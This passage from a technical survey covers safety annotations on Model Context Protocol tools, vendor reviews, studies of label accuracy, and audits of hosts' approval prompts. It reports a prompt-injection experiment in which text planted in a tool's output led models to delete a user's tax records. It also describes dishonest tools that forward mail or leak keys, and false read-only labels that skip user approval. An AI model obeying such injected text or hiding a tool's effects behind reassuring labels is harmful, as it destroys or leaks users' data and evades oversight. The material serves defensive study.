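The rules also make labels more informative. Anthropic rejects any tool that can both fetch and change data depending on a parameter, even if its description documents the difference. One label covers everything a tool can do, so such a tool would have to be labeled destructive even when the agent only wanted to read. Splitting the tool gives each part an accurate label.

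The review does less to establish that an annotation is true. Anthropic's criteria require each description to match the tool's actual behaviour, but by default a server enters the directory with a "Community" label after an automatic scan for policy compliance. Anthropic may choose listings it expects to be highly useful and give them a slower review, in which people run a functional test of each tool. These listings can earn the label "Verified". The developer supplies the server's web address, documentation and answers to questions, and the submission steps don't ask for source code. A functional test can catch a "read-only" tool that visibly changes the test account, but not a server that sends a copy of the results to another machine. Anthropic warns that "Verification isn't a security audit", and tools run the same way in Claude under either label.

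OpenAI asks developers to justify the annotation values in writing. OpenAI's *Remote MCP server review requirements* lists hints that don't appear to match a tool's behaviour among the common reasons for rejection. If a server sends `readOnlyHint: false` for a tool that the developer describes as "functionally read-only", the developer has to correct the annotation on the server and have OpenAI scan it again, because an explanation isn't enough. OpenAI may use automated scans or manual reviews, and its reviewers need a working demo account and test cases that produce the promised results.

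After publication, OpenAI periodically fetches each server's tool definitions again and compares them with the published ones. A new tool becomes available only after it passes automated checks, and a changed definition replaces the old one only after it passes too. This catches a developer who quietly rewrites a label or description. But OpenAI keeps a copy of the definition, not the server's code, and calls go to the live server. A developer could pass review with an accurately described search_mail and add the forwarding the next day. The comparison would find nothing, because the change affects A and leaves D the same.

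OpenAI and Anthropic also define the hints slightly differently. The protocol's schema contrasts destructive changes with ones that only add something, so a developer could reasonably set destructiveHint to false for send_mail. OpenAI asks for true, because nobody can undo a sent message. Anthropic asks for true on tools that "modify or delete data", which doesn't settle whether sending a message counts. A host can't tell from the value which definition the developer used.

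The definition of openWorldHint matters more for prompt injection. OpenAI tells developers to set it to false for a tool limited to a private account, even when an outside company hosts the service. By that rule, a correctly annotated search_mail tool is closed-world. But strangers write much of the text in a mailbox, and a host that inspected only the output of open-world tools would let their instructions through unchecked. The protocol's maintainers advise treating anything external to a tool as a possible source of untrusted content, but a value of false gives the host no reason to do so here.

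### The case for annotations

Most server authors are presumably honest, and annotations on their tools can improve safety with almost no extra effort. If an assistant makes twenty calls to answer a question and eighteen of them are searches, a host that uses accurate annotations prompts the user twice instead of twenty times, so the user is more likely to read both prompts. A company that runs its own servers can base its rules on the annotations because it controls the code. GitHub offers a read-only mode for its tools, and about 17% of its users turn it on, according to the Model Context Protocol maintainers.

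Annotations can also feed a policy engine, a program in the host that applies fixed rules to tool calls. The maintainers suggest a rule that blocks open-world tools once the session has accessed private data. In the office assistant, this rule would take effect once search_mail returned the morning's messages. If a hidden instruction then led the model to propose sending invoices to an outside address, the host would block the call without having to recognise the injection. Although the labels only describe the tools, the host enforces the rule, which protects against a misled model when the tools are labelled honestly. The rule would also block the message to Maria unless the user could approve an exception.

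The existing hints can't fully support such a rule, because none of them marks data as private. By March 2026, contributors had filed five proposals for new annotations or closely related features. Three would each add one hint (secretHint, unsafeOutputHint and trustedHint), and a fourth would add a broader set for governance and user interfaces. Jonathan Hefner, a maintainer, objected to an early draft of the broader set because he couldn't see how the annotations would change a client's behavior.

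The fifth proposal, *Trust and Sensitivity Annotations*, came from contributors at GitHub and OpenAI, who had run into gaps while using the protocol in production. It would label the data in requests and responses as well as the tools. Labels on tools alone are too coarse. In a discussion on GitHub, one developer wanted GitHub's server to let an agent read public code repositories without extra permission, but the same tool also reads private ones, so a single permission had to cover both. Kapil Sharma of Microsoft submitted experimental code, *added initial scaffolding files with python ref SDK*, that lets servers label data as medical, personal or financial, or as containing credentials. Servers could also declare where data comes from and goes to, and how severe the outcome of a call might be.

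According to a third-party blog on the protocol (2026), the proposal's rules allow a session's sensitivity to rise but never fall. A host can accept a confidential or untrusted label from any server because the label only adds checks. No server can remove those checks by declaring its own output harmless. A dishonest server could still leave its output unmarked, so a cautious host would have to treat unmarked data as sensitive.

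None of these labels is close to becoming part of the standard. In April 2026, Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter* set up a group to examine the proposals together and recommend changes, but not to make them. The charter listed the trust and sensitivity proposal, the broader set, and a proposal for preflight checks as drafts. The group is also considering annotations that could change from one call to the next. By late November, the project's index of proposals listed no tool-annotation proposal as accepted or final.

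Tool annotations are also not among the five priority areas that the Model Context Protocol (2026) project announced in August for faster review. The roadmap that the Model Context Protocol (2026) maintainers updated on 16 November mentions only annotations that label the intended audience and priority of content, and it raises the possibility of dropping them because few developers use them. Proposals for the March 2027 revision must be final by about mid-January, so labels for trust and sensitivity will probably have to wait until September 2027 at the earliest. Until then, servers can put such labels in a general-purpose metadata field, but off-the-shelf hosts won't act on fields they don't recognise.

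## What surveys of published tools find

A host can safely use annotations only if developers write them and they are accurate. Several teams surveyed published MCP tools in 2026. Counting annotations is easy because every server sends its tool definitions to any client that requests them. Checking whether a definition is true requires the source code, and even that shows only what a tool could do. Finding out what it does requires running it, which few surveys have tried.

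### How many tools have annotations

The official MCP registry is a public list of servers that anyone can add to. *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (Afsar, 2026) reports on 400 servers drawn at random from 7,258 that run on the user's own machine and come from npm, the main library of JavaScript packages. Afsar started each server once, without repairing it or supplying credentials, and requested its list of tools. Of the 400, 195 ran, 150 failed to complete the opening exchange with the client, 53 needed credentials, and two had unavailable packages.

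In *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, Trofimov and Novikov (2026) counted annotations on remote servers, which run on their operators' machines. They contacted all 9,234 remote servers in a July snapshot of the registry, and 4,838 returned tools. Shi, Fu and colleagues (2026) did a smaller count in *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions*, using tools from 100 servers with many GitHub stars.

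| Sample | Tools | Share without annotations |
|---|---|---|
| Afsar, random local servers | 2,766 | 58.8% |
| Trofimov and Novikov, all responding remote servers | 98,291 | 26.0% |
| Trofimov and Novikov, without the largest publisher | 54,064 | 47.2% |
| Shi, Fu and colleagues, starred GitHub servers | 1,856 | 82.5% |

A single publisher accounts for much of the spread. It runs 1,274 of the remote servers that responded, and every one of its 44,227 tools, 45% of the total, has all four hints set. About 25,500 tools in the census have no annotations, all from other publishers. They make up 26.0% of all 98,291 tools but 47.2% of the 54,064 tools from other publishers.

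The remaining gap between 47.2% and Afsar's 58.8% may be partly chance. In Afsar's sample, 72 servers annotated every tool, 122 annotated none, and none annotated only some. Tools on the same server are therefore not independent observations, and the effective sample size is closer to the 194 servers than to the 2,766 tools. One server supplied 300 of the tools. In the sample, 63% of servers had no annotations, with a margin of error of about seven percentage points. The gap may also reflect a real difference between local and remote servers, and Afsar's npm servers represent less than a third of the registry.

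Choosing well-known servers can raise or lower the share of tools found to lack annotations. Afsar also tested a hand-picked set of 24 reference and popular community servers, where 41.5% of tools lacked annotations. Afsar attributes this lower rate to the reference servers, which tend to have them. But the starred servers on GitHub had the highest rate of any sample. That sample may be older, since Shi, Fu and colleagues searched vulnerability records in February 2026, and annotations could have become more common since then.

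In a host that follows the protocol's defaults, a missing annotation causes an extra prompt for the user and does no other harm. The values that developers set matter more. Trofimov and Novikov found destructiveHint on 65.8% of tools, but mostly on tools also marked read-only, where it has no meaning. Only 12.9% of all tools had a destructiveHint that applied, and 3.1% of all tools had one set to true. So when developers classified a tool that can write, they called it non-destructive about three times out of four. Leaving out the largest publisher hardly changes these shares.

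More than 3.1% of tools may be destructive. The 26.0% without annotations could do anything, and Trofimov and Novikov didn't call any tools, so they can't tell whether the labels are right. Many of the non-destructive labels may well be accurate, though, because a tool that only adds a calendar entry destroys nothing.

Templates also seem to determine many of the values. Each of the four hints can be true, false or missing, and 66 of the 81 possible combinations occur in the census. The most common combination marks a tool as read-only, non-destructive, idempotent and open-world. It covers 39.9% of all tools, but only 7.3% when the largest publisher is excluded. A host that reads this combination may be reading a publisher's standard settings rather than values someone chose for that tool.

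### Whether descriptions match the code

Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, compared 19,200 tools from 2,214 Python servers with their source code. They count a tool's name, text and input schema as its description, since the model sees all three. They write Φ for what a tool is for and Ψ for its effects on its surroundings, and they call the tool inconsistent if

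Φ_claim ≠ Φ_act or Ψ_act ⊈ Ψ_claim.

The second condition is a failure of A ⊆ D, the requirement that a tool's actual effects stay within its declared ones. The first is stricter, because a tool that does less than its description promises also counts as inconsistent. Shi, Zhang and colleagues divide the two conditions into seven types, four for function and three for side effects. Applied to search_mail, they might look like this:

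| Type | Example | Does the tool do more than declared? |
|---|---|---|
| Undeclared functionality | It also searches the user's cloud files | Yes |
| Overclaimed functionality | The description mentions archived mail, but the code never searches it | Usually not |
| Misclaimed functionality | It deletes messages instead of finding them | Yes |
| Ambiguous functionality | The description is only "Handle mail" | Unclear |
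| Resource overconsumption | It indexes the whole disk before each search | Yes |
| State mutation | It changes who may open the mailbox | Yes |
| Data leakage | It uploads the user's query to an outside server | Yes |

Their program, DCIChecker, works in two stages. It first finds each tool in the source code and gathers the function that runs when an agent calls it, the project's own helper functions up to three calls deep, and any sensitive operations, such as network requests or file deletions. A language model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, then compares this code with the tool's description twice, once to judge whether they agree and once to look for a mismatch. If the answers differ, even if only about the type of mismatch, a third prompt presents both arguments for a decision.

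The wording of the prompt makes a large difference. On 400 real tools that the researchers labelled by hand, the first prompt alone found only 47% of the mismatches. The second found all of them, but 21% of its alarms were false. The full procedure flagged 97.46% of the inconsistent tools (its recall), and 96.00% of the tools it flagged were inconsistent (its precision).

That recall figure is too high for the collection as a whole. The 400 tools consisted of 200 that DCIChecker had flagged and 200 that it had passed. The researchers found eight false alarms and five misses, which gives a recall of 192/197 in this sample. In the full collection, however, DCIChecker passed about eight times as many tools as it flagged, so misses make up a larger share of the inconsistent tools. If 2.5% of the passed tools are inconsistent there, as in the sample, DCIChecker missed about 380 and its recall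 was closer to 83%. Five misses are too few for a precise estimate and are compatible with a recall anywhere from about 68% to 94%.

DCIChecker flagged 1,907 of the 19,200 tools as inconsistent, which is 9.93% of the total and 11.2% of the 17,030 that had a usable description to check. Most of the other 2,170 had no description. This can happen by accident, because the Python toolkit takes the description from a comment in the code and leaves it empty if the developer wrote none. Inconsistent tools turned up on 35% of the servers, but 183 servers, about 8% of the total, account for 60% of the inconsistent tools.

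Most of these tools would not cause a gate to allow something harmful. Mismatched functionality makes up 75.2% of cases, and the largest single type, overclaimed functionality, makes up 35.4%. Undeclared side effects, which include state changes, data leaks and excessive use of resources, make up 24.8%, or about 470 tools. DCIChecker assigned each tool only one main type, but a tool can have several faults, so between about 470 and 1,907 tools do more than they declare, roughly 3% to 11% of the tools with descriptions.

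Some individual cases are serious. One tool is described as converting a "local PDF file", but its code uploads the file to an outside service. Another is supposed to only repeat a message, but it also adds a secret key from the server's environment to its reply, so the key enters the model's context. Even an overclaim can be dangerous if it concerns a safeguard. One tool that places orders on a trading exchange is described as requiring the user's approval for each order, but its code submits the order immediately. An agent or user who relied on that description would have no reason to add their own check.

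Shi, Zhang and colleagues don't accuse the developers of malice, and outdated or careless documentation could explain many of the cases. Their method can't confirm what remote tools do, because it analyzes published source code and the operator of a remote server can run different code.

### Whether the annotations are true

DCIChecker tests descriptions and ignores the annotation fields. If delete_file had an honest description and a false read-only label, DCIChecker would pass it.

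In *When Neither Side Confirms*, Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026) came closest to testing the fields. They ran an automatic filter on 1,000 code repositories listed in the registry to pick out possibly destructive tools by their names, descriptions, labels and confirmation steps. Two language models, GPT-6.1 Sol and Gemini 4 Argon, then read the code behind a sample of 366 tools, and a third model settled their disagreements. The models classed 269 of the tools as destructive, meaning that some call could irreversibly delete or overwrite data, send messages, move money or run arbitrary commands.

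Yao and colleagues estimate that 70% of destructive tools (95% interval 43% to 88%) have neither a destructive label nor a confirmation step on the server. Another 20% have only the label. This fits the census of remote servers, where developers rarely marked anything as destructive. Most of these omissions would not cause a host that follows the protocol's defaults to misclassify the tool.

Falsely reassuring labels are rarer. About 5.4% of the destructive tools were labelled read-only or non-destructive and had no confirmation step to protect the user. A host that follows the defaults and relies on the labels would run these tools without asking the user to confirm. The figure covers only tools that the filter selected, and the filter missed most destructive tools. Including the missed ones raises the share to at least 10.6%.

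Some of those labels may be defensible, because Yao and colleagues count sending a message as destructive and the protocol's own definition doesn't clearly include it. Two people checked 60 of the classified tools. They were sure about 56 and agreed with the models' classifications on 51 of those. The models had classified the other five as destructive, but the people considered their actions reversible or harmless.

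The 5.4% is the share of destructive tools that have a reassuring label, but a host deciding whether to skip a prompt needs to know what share of reassuring labels are false. That share also depends on how many harmless tools have the same label. Measuring it would require checking the code behind each tool in a random sample of those labelled read-only, which none of these surveys did.

### How tools change after publication

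A label that was accurate when the user approved a server can become false later. Bharti (2026), in *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly*, followed 19,099 servers through 120 snapshots of the registry between 30 April and 28 July. Three quarters of the entries never changed. On a typical day about 1.5% did, which might suggest that

1 − (1 − 0.01465)³⁰ ≈ 36%

of entries would change within a month. The measured share was only 11.9%, because the formula assumes that each change affects a different server. In fact, the most active 5% of servers made 61% of the changes. Just 3.3% of descriptions changed within 30 days.

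Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, reports that of 8,900 servers with more than one published version, 51.1% changed their description, packages or network address between versions. This higher rate is compatible with Bharti's result because Kraishan leaves out servers with only one version. Among all 21,643 servers in the registry, the share is 21%, close to the quarter that changed in Bharti's data.

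Changes often come early. Among the servers in Kraishan's data that changed, the median time to the first change was less than a day. Bharti followed one group of new servers for ten weeks and found that their rate of change fell by about two thirds. A user who installs a newly published server is therefore approving it when its entry is most likely to change.

Kraishan calls a change silent if the text or the destination changes while every identifier stays the same, and 40.6% of the multi-version servers made at least one silent change. Many of these changes are rewritten descriptions, which could be corrections. The 370 servers (4.2%) that moved their remote address to a different host are more worrying. Most of them probably changed hosting provider, but a hostile takeover would look the same in the registry. Servers with silent changes also had about three times the odds of a serious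 security warning from Kraishan's code scanner. However, only 56% of the warnings that Kraishan checked by hand were correct, and the association doesn't show that one problem causes the other.

Neither study measures how often a tool's own definition changes. The descriptions in Bharti's data are summaries of whole servers, limited to 100 characters, and none of the 72,606 version records that Kraishan collected includes a tool definition. A host therefore can't use the registry to detect that a tool it approved last month has a new description, or that the tool's readOnlyHint has changed from false to true. According to Kraishan, the protocol also doesn't notify installed clients when a server's address moves to another host.

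A host can detect some changes for itself by keeping a fingerprint, or hash, of each approved definition and comparing it with what the server sends later. Bharti recommends the same method for services that screen registry descriptions, along with regular checks of the whole list. Rechecking just the 5% of servers that have changed most in the past would catch only about 20% of the already listed servers whose descriptions change next.

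Comparing tool definitions, as OpenAI does for its directory, misses changes in the code behind them. To look for such changes, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *ProbeID*, sent test inputs to tools on 16 published servers, recorded the responses, and repeated the test eleven times over eleven weeks while keeping the version numbers fixed. Ignoring details that normally vary, such as timestamps, they found that 7 of the 59 tools returned something different from the original response, three of them after the same version was reinstalled. A different response isn't necessarily harmful, but the results show that a tool's behaviour can change while its version number stays the same.

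ProbeID turns this test into a check that a host could run before using a tool. It keeps a bank of inputs with trusted responses, sends the tool a secret random selection of those inputs, and rejects the tool if its responses differ too much from the trusted ones. In one experiment, two altered tools passed no matter how many inputs ProbeID sent, because no input in the bank triggered the altered behaviour. Chen and colleagues also acknowledge that the method can't detect side effects that never appear in a response. For example, a search_mail tool that started forwarding messages would pass if it still returned the correct search results.

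Detecting that kind of leak requires monitoring the network while the tool runs. *MCP-SandboxScan* (2026) describes a small test that runs tools in a sandbox and compares their network traffic with their metadata. In five cases the metadata indicated outside traffic and the sandbox recorded some. In 14 the metadata indicated traffic but none occurred, and in ten there was neither. At least one repository produced traffic that its metadata didn't indicate. The description may have been incomplete, or the program that interpreted it may have made a mistake. The 14 cases without the expected traffic show how much a single run can miss. For example, a search_mail tool that forwarded only messages containing the word "invoice" would send nothing during a test on other mail.

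## What audits of hosts and frameworks find

Labeling a tool as destructive protects users only if some program acts on the label. Both the server and the host can ask the user before an irreversible call, but the Model Context Protocol specification requires neither to do so. Yao and colleagues read the source code of servers and hosts in 2026 and found that each side mostly relies on the other to ask. They assumed that both were honest, so their results cover cases where a model calls a destructive tool by mistake or because of injected text.

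### Confirmation by the server

The official registry listed 29,242 GitHub repositories, of which 17,554 were original, unarchived public projects in Python, TypeScript or JavaScript. Yao and colleagues took the 200 with the most stars and drew 800 of the rest at random. Each random repository stands for (17,554 − 200)/800 ≈ 22 repositories in the estimates, while a starred one stands only for itself, so the results mainly describe little-known servers. The destructive tools fall into five tiers, according to what the server does on a typical call under its default settings:

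| Tier | What the server does before acting | Estimated share of destructive tools |
|---|---|---|
| T0 | Nothing, and the tool has no destructive label | 70% |
| T1 | Nothing, but the tool has a destructive label | 20% |
| T2 | Requires a confirmation that the model can supply itself | 8.9% |
| T3 | Asks the user if the host can pass on the question, and otherwise goes ahead | 0.2% |
| T4 | Refuses unless a human has answered | 0.5% |

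An estimated 90% of destructive tools (95% interval 82% to 95%) therefore act as soon as the server receives the call. Much of this estimate depends on a small follow-up sample. The automatic filter had missed 83% of destructive tools, so the models that classified the code also listed every tool in 40 of the repositories, and Yao and colleagues added the missed ones. The overall estimate stays between 87% and 91% if any one of the repositories with missed tools is left out. The split between labelled and unlabelled tools is much less certain.

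### Elicitation

The protocol gives servers one way to reach the user, called elicitation, in which the host passes on a question from the server. Suppose delete_file uses it. The model proposes deleting a spreadsheet, the host forwards the call, and the server returns an unfinished result containing a question. The host shows the question as a form and sends back the user's answer, and the server then deletes the file or stops. The server has to put its question in a result because the July 2026 revision no longer lets servers start requests themselves, according to the Model Context Protocol documentation for Ruby.

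The Model Context Protocol (2026) specification requires a host to declare which kinds of elicitation request it supports, and forbids servers to send any other kind. If a host doesn't support elicitation, a server connected to it can't ask the user for input through the protocol. The specification doesn't define whether the server should then go ahead or refuse.

Only 36 of the 1,000 repositories mention elicitation. In 19 of them, Yao and colleagues found 168 tools that by default ask the user before a destructive action. When the host can't relay the question to the user, 38 of these tools refuse, 30 go ahead, and 100 accept a confirmation from the model instead. So 77% of the tools can proceed without the user's approval.

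One database server in the registry has a tool that asks for confirmation before deleting a whole database, but deletes it anyway if it can't ask. Some developers choose such behaviour on purpose. The developers of a server for the mapping program QGIS turned off its confirmation step by default "because MCP clients gate destructive tool calls themselves".

### What hosts do by default

Most of the hosts that Yao and colleagues examined do not do this. Their sample contains 41 popular open-source hosts, of which 25 are applications, such as coding agents, chat programs and workflow platforms, and 16 are software development kits (SDKs), which are libraries for building agents. An AI coding agent traced the path of an ordinary tool call through each host's source code, assuming a fresh installation. A second agent, from a different company, traced 20 of the hosts and reached the same result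 as the first for each.

| Default before an ordinary MCP tool call | Applications | SDKs |
|---|---|---|
| The host asks the user | 7 | 0 |
| The host decides from the tool's annotations | 1 | 0 |
| A language model classifies the call | 1 | 0 |
| No approval step | 16 | 16 |

The 32 hosts without an approval step include Cline, LibreChat, n8n and the OpenAI Agents SDK. Only six of the 32 show elicitation questions to the user by default, and Cline and LibreChat are not among them. If a user connects the database server to either one, the model can delete a database without anyone being asked.

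In 39 of the 41 hosts, a destructive label changed nothing. Hosts that prompt would have prompted anyway, and hosts that don't prompt ignore the label. The two exceptions are Qwen Code, which uses the classifier, and Codex CLI, OpenAI's command-line coding agent. Codex CLI runs a tool without asking if its labels meet either of two conditions:

- read-only and not destructive
- non-destructive and closed-world

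Codex CLI asks for approval before running any other tool, including one with no labels. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* adds that a tool labeled destructive always needs approval, even if it is also labeled read-only. But both conditions for skipping approval depend on reassuring labels, which a host should accept only from an author it trusts. If the author of delete_file declared it non-destructive and closed-world, Codex CLI would run it without asking.

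VS Code, Microsoft's code editor, ignores the destructive label but acts on the read-only one. It prompts before a tool call unless the tool is marked read-only or its server runs in a sandbox. Microsoft's *Integrate MCP servers with Copilot* tells server authors not to assume that readOnlyHint bypasses approval, because annotations describe behaviour and are "not permission grants". On the default path that Yao and colleagues traced, however, a read-only label lets a tool run without approval, even if the label is false.

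Most applications outside this group of popular hosts also lack approval steps. Majeed, Mahmoud and Nadi (2026), in *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications*, used a language model to classify 1,723 MCP applications on GitHub, each with at least ten stars. Of these, 37.2% have an approval step that blocks the call. That figure may overstate protection, because an application counts if its code contains such a step, even if the step is off by default. Users can switch servers or tools on and off in advance in 77.2% of applications, but this controls only which tools are available. Neither control is present in 20.0%.

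### Injected deletions and the confirmation flag

Yao and colleagues also ran seven of the hosts against a harmless test server with two tools, list_notes and delete_note. When the user asked to delete one note, opencode (a coding agent) and four SDKs deleted it without a confirmation prompt, although delete_note was labeled destructive.

In the injection test, the user asked an agent to list the notes and delete an old draft. The returned list included an added instruction to delete the tax records too. Yao and colleagues tried four phrasings of this instruction on five cheap models through four SDKs, five times each, in three setups. In the first, the server had only the destructive label. In the other two, it also required the argument confirm=true before it would delete anything, and the injected text mentioned that argument in only one of them.

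DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash never tried to delete the tax records. The other four models deleted them in 479 of 960 runs:

| Setup | Attempts in 320 runs | Deletions | Deletions per run |
|---|---|---|---|
| Label only | 180 | 180 | 56% |
| Flag required, injected text doesn't mention it | 169 | 127 | 40% |
| Flag required, injected text mentions it | 175 | 172 | 54% |

The label stopped none of the attempts. The flag stopped a quarter of them when the attacker's text left it out and almost none when the text included it. An attacker is unlikely to leave the flag out, because the tool's published definition names it.

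A flag of this kind is an argument of the call, so the model sets it. Text that can make the model propose a deletion can also make it set the flag. Even a model that resists injection may set the flag without the user's agreement. When DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash carried out the deletion the user had requested, it set the flag on its first call in 135 of 160 runs, before the server had asked for it and without consulting the user. The server receives the same value whether or not a human has agreed. The 100 eliciting tools that fall back to a confirmation from the model have this weakness.

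The choice of model affected the number of deletions far more than the choice of SDK. GPT-4o-mini deleted the tax records in 215 of its 240 runs and Gemma 4 in only 10, while the number of deletions per SDK ranged from 105 to 126. The tests included no flagship model, and a stronger model would probably have attempted fewer deletions. But on the server with only the label, the model was the only protection, because every attempted deletion succeeded.

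### What would close the gap

Yao and colleagues paired each of their 269 destructive tools with each of 41 hosts and worked out whether the host or the tool's server would require a human to approve the call. In 74.9% of all pairs, and 60.7% of pairs with the 25 hosts that are applications, neither would. These figures are close to the shares of hosts without an approval step (78% and 64%), because servers rarely require approval themselves.

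The result depends largely on which hosts are included. Adding seven closed-source applications, among them Claude Code and Cursor, lowers the figure for applications from 60.7% to 47.5%. Both 0.607 × 25 and 0.475 × 32 come to about 15.2, so those seven contribute almost no unapproved pairs, although Yao and colleagues took their behaviour from documentation instead of source code. The percentages also give every host equal weight, however many people use it.

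They then calculated what three changes in default behaviour would do. For the 25 applications, the results are:

| Change | Destructive, runs unapproved | Destructive, server refuses | Harmless, user is asked |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 60.7% | 0.7% | 32.5% |
| Every host passes on elicitation questions | 56.7% | 0.0% | 35.2% |
| Every host prompts unless a label says read-only or non-destructive | 5.4% | 0.7% | 82.6% |
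| Every destructive tool refuses without a human answer | 0.0% | 71.0% | 32.5% |

Supporting elicitation in every host would achieve little, because so few tools use it. If every destructive tool required an answer, most of them would be unusable, because most hosts can't pass the question to the user. Some tools would refuse to run even after the user had approved the action, because a server can't tell whether the host has already prompted. Yao and colleagues suggest letting hosts declare that they obtain human approval, but the server would then have to rely on the host's declaration.

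The change in host prompts closes most of the gap, mainly by treating unlabelled tools as dangerous. The remaining 5.4% corresponds to the destructive tools that have a reassuring label and no confirmation step, which a gate that checks only labels can't catch.

Authors wrote these labels when few hosts used them. If every host skipped the prompt for tools labelled safe, a dishonest author could avoid it by changing one word. The 5.4% therefore probably reflects carelessness and differing definitions, and it could rise once attackers can benefit from false labels. Prompting for every tool not labelled read-only would catch destructive tools wrongly labelled non-destructive, but users would see more prompts.

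Among harmless tools that the filter had picked out as possibly destructive, the share of pairs in which the host interrupts the user would rise from 32.5% to 82.6%. The share would probably be lower for harmless tools in general, since only about a quarter of the tools in the largest census had no annotations. Even so, users of the 16 applications that now show no prompts would see them frequently.

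### Whether people read what they approve

These audits count an approval step if it exists, whether or not anyone reads the prompt. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an experiment in which the company paid 1,053 professional testers to do coding work with Claude Code. Partway through each session, it replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Testers refused the command 13.6% of the time. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after fifty or more prompts.

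An automatic classifier blocked 89.0% of the same commands. Testers caught only six that the classifier had let through, so requiring both checks would have raised the total to 89.6%. Since August, Claude Code has used the classifier in place of most prompts by default on individual and team plans. Anthropic had an interest in this result, and testers in an artificial environment had less to lose than developers working on their own files. The company still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves, even though testers added little to the classifier's result.

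In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated assistant on an everyday task. Seven of its 18 actions went beyond what the user had requested. Participants who had to approve every action allowed 96 of 238 overreaching actions, or 40.3%. About a third of them let the assistant permanently delete an old timesheet that nobody had asked it to delete. These participants refused more often than Anthropic's testers, possibly because the descriptions were in plain language and the session lasted only minutes.

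Yan also tested two ways to reduce the number of prompts. In one group a model approved some actions and passed the rest to the participant. In another, participants set standing rules in advance for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data:

| Group | Average number of prompts | Overreach approved when asked |
|---|---|---|
| Approves every action | 18.0 | 40.3% |
| Model passes on some actions | 10.0 | 46.1% |
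| Standing rules set in advance | 10.9 | 66.8% |

Neither group with fewer prompts was more careful. This weakens one argument for annotations, that users will read prompts more closely if they see fewer, but doesn't refute it, because 18 prompts may be too few to tire anybody. Participants also chose "ask" for 114 of the 140 standing rules, so the rules settled little.

*Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) reports how 107 practitioners answered questions about permissions. Of these, 47.7% said they read permission requests carefully, 33.6% said they skim them and 20.6% said they approve them by default. A third said they had become less careful over time. Nearly all (98.1%) were more willing to grant read-only access than other kinds. A false read-only label may therefore make users less careful even if the host prompts them, provided that the host displays the label.

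Some developers may be supervising in a different way. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) cites usage data in which experienced Claude Code users turned on automatic approval more often than others but also interrupted the agent more often. Interrupting can work when the user is watching and the mistake is reversible, but it is little help against a single call that sends the invoices to a stranger.

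Even users who read each prompt carefully can make bad decisions. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) argues that an action can be acceptable on its own and still complete something the user has ruled out. A user might approve copying invoices into a folder and later approve sharing that folder with a supplier, without noticing that the two steps together disclose every customer's bill. The paper proposes prompts that describe the combined effect of the pending action and the earlier ones.

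### Whether the approved call is the one that runs

Even when someone reads a tool call carefully before approving it, the runtime, the program that executes an agent's steps, may also execute a different call. *Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) audited ten agent runtimes and could test eight of them for this problem. Three executed only what the approver had seen. One resisted changes made through its normal interface but not changes made directly in its database. In the other four, the call could be changed between approval and execution. LangGraph and Agno, for example, run whatever arguments are in the saved state when the agent resumes, so anyone able to change that state can turn an approved payment into a different one.

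It also matters a lot where the prompt's text comes from. Kodathala and colleagues asked 15 language models to act as approvers. In one test, the user wanted a report sent to their boss, and a compromised agent added a hidden second recipient. All 15 models approved the email when they read the agent's own description of it, but refused when they read a summary that trusted code had generated from the actual call. Over a wider set of attacks, the generated summary raised the share caught from 30% to 98%, though the models also refused 16% of harmless requests that resembled attacks. No people took part, so it is unknown how much the summary would help human approvers.

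Elicitation is weak against a dishonest server because the server writes the question. The protocol's Python library passes the text on unchanged, and Kodathala and colleagues produced identical questions for a payment of 10 and a payment of 10,000 to a different account. Elicitation is a real safeguard against a misled model when the server is honest, but a dishonest server's question is just another declared effect that nobody has checked. A summary generated from the call doesn't fix this, since it shows the arguments and not what the tool's code will do with them.

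### Frameworks that leave the check to developers

A host could also check arguments with a fixed rule instead of a prompt. In June 2026, Mellafe Zuvic looked for such checks in the public code of three products for building agents. LangChain (with its companion LangGraph) and LlamaIndex are general-purpose frameworks, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit lets agents work with accounts at the payment company Stripe. A qualifying check had to examine the concrete argument values after the model proposed a call and before the tool ran, and block the call if the values broke a rule or the check itself failed.

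LangChain, LlamaIndex and Stripe's toolkit all control which tools the model can use, but none authorises argument values by default. LangChain looks up the requested tool by name, usually checks that the arguments have the right form, and runs the tool. Developers can attach code that observes each call, but that code cannot reliably stop it. LlamaIndex works in much the same way. Stripe's toolkit adds a fixed list of permitted actions and supports keys with restricted rights, but within those limits it forwards whatever amount, customer or payment reference the model supplies.

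Checking an argument's format doesn't prevent a redirected payout, because an attacker's account number is as well formed as the merchant's. Mellafe Zuvic tested this case with a mock shop and a scripted model output that changed the payout account to an attacker's. LangChain's ordinary code path made the change, while ScopeGate, the author's own gate, refused the same call because the account wasn't on the operator's list. The test shows how the framework handles a bad proposal, but it doesn't measure how often a model would make one. The audit also doesn't cover any checks that Stripe performs on its own servers.

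Mellafe Zuvic describes the missing check as a documented design choice that makes developers who build on a framework responsible for adding it. Yao and colleagues found the same division of labour in the 16 SDKs they examined. Seven offer a dedicated approval option that is off by default, five offer only a general hook that runs before each call, and four offer neither. This division is reasonable because LangChain's developers can't know which accounts belong to a shop or whom an office assistant may write to, so somebody closer to the application has to write P.

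A framework can't supply the rule, but it doesn't have to run the call when no rule exists. It could refuse calls to payment or deletion tools until the developer has either written a rule or explicitly waived it, in line with Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults. Developers would find this annoying, and some would waive the rule without thinking. At present they don't have to make that decision, and in the survey by Majeed and colleagues, 62.8% of applications had no approval step to make up for a missing rule.

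## Incidents in which honest tools were misused

When no program checks a call, the outcome depends on what the model proposes. Since 2025, agents have leaked private data and deleted company records using tools that did exactly what their definitions described. A ⊆ D therefore held, but the effects went beyond what the user was willing to allow. Each incident can be used to assess both declarations and enforcement by asking what accurate labels or a narrower grant of authority would have changed.

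### The lethal trifecta

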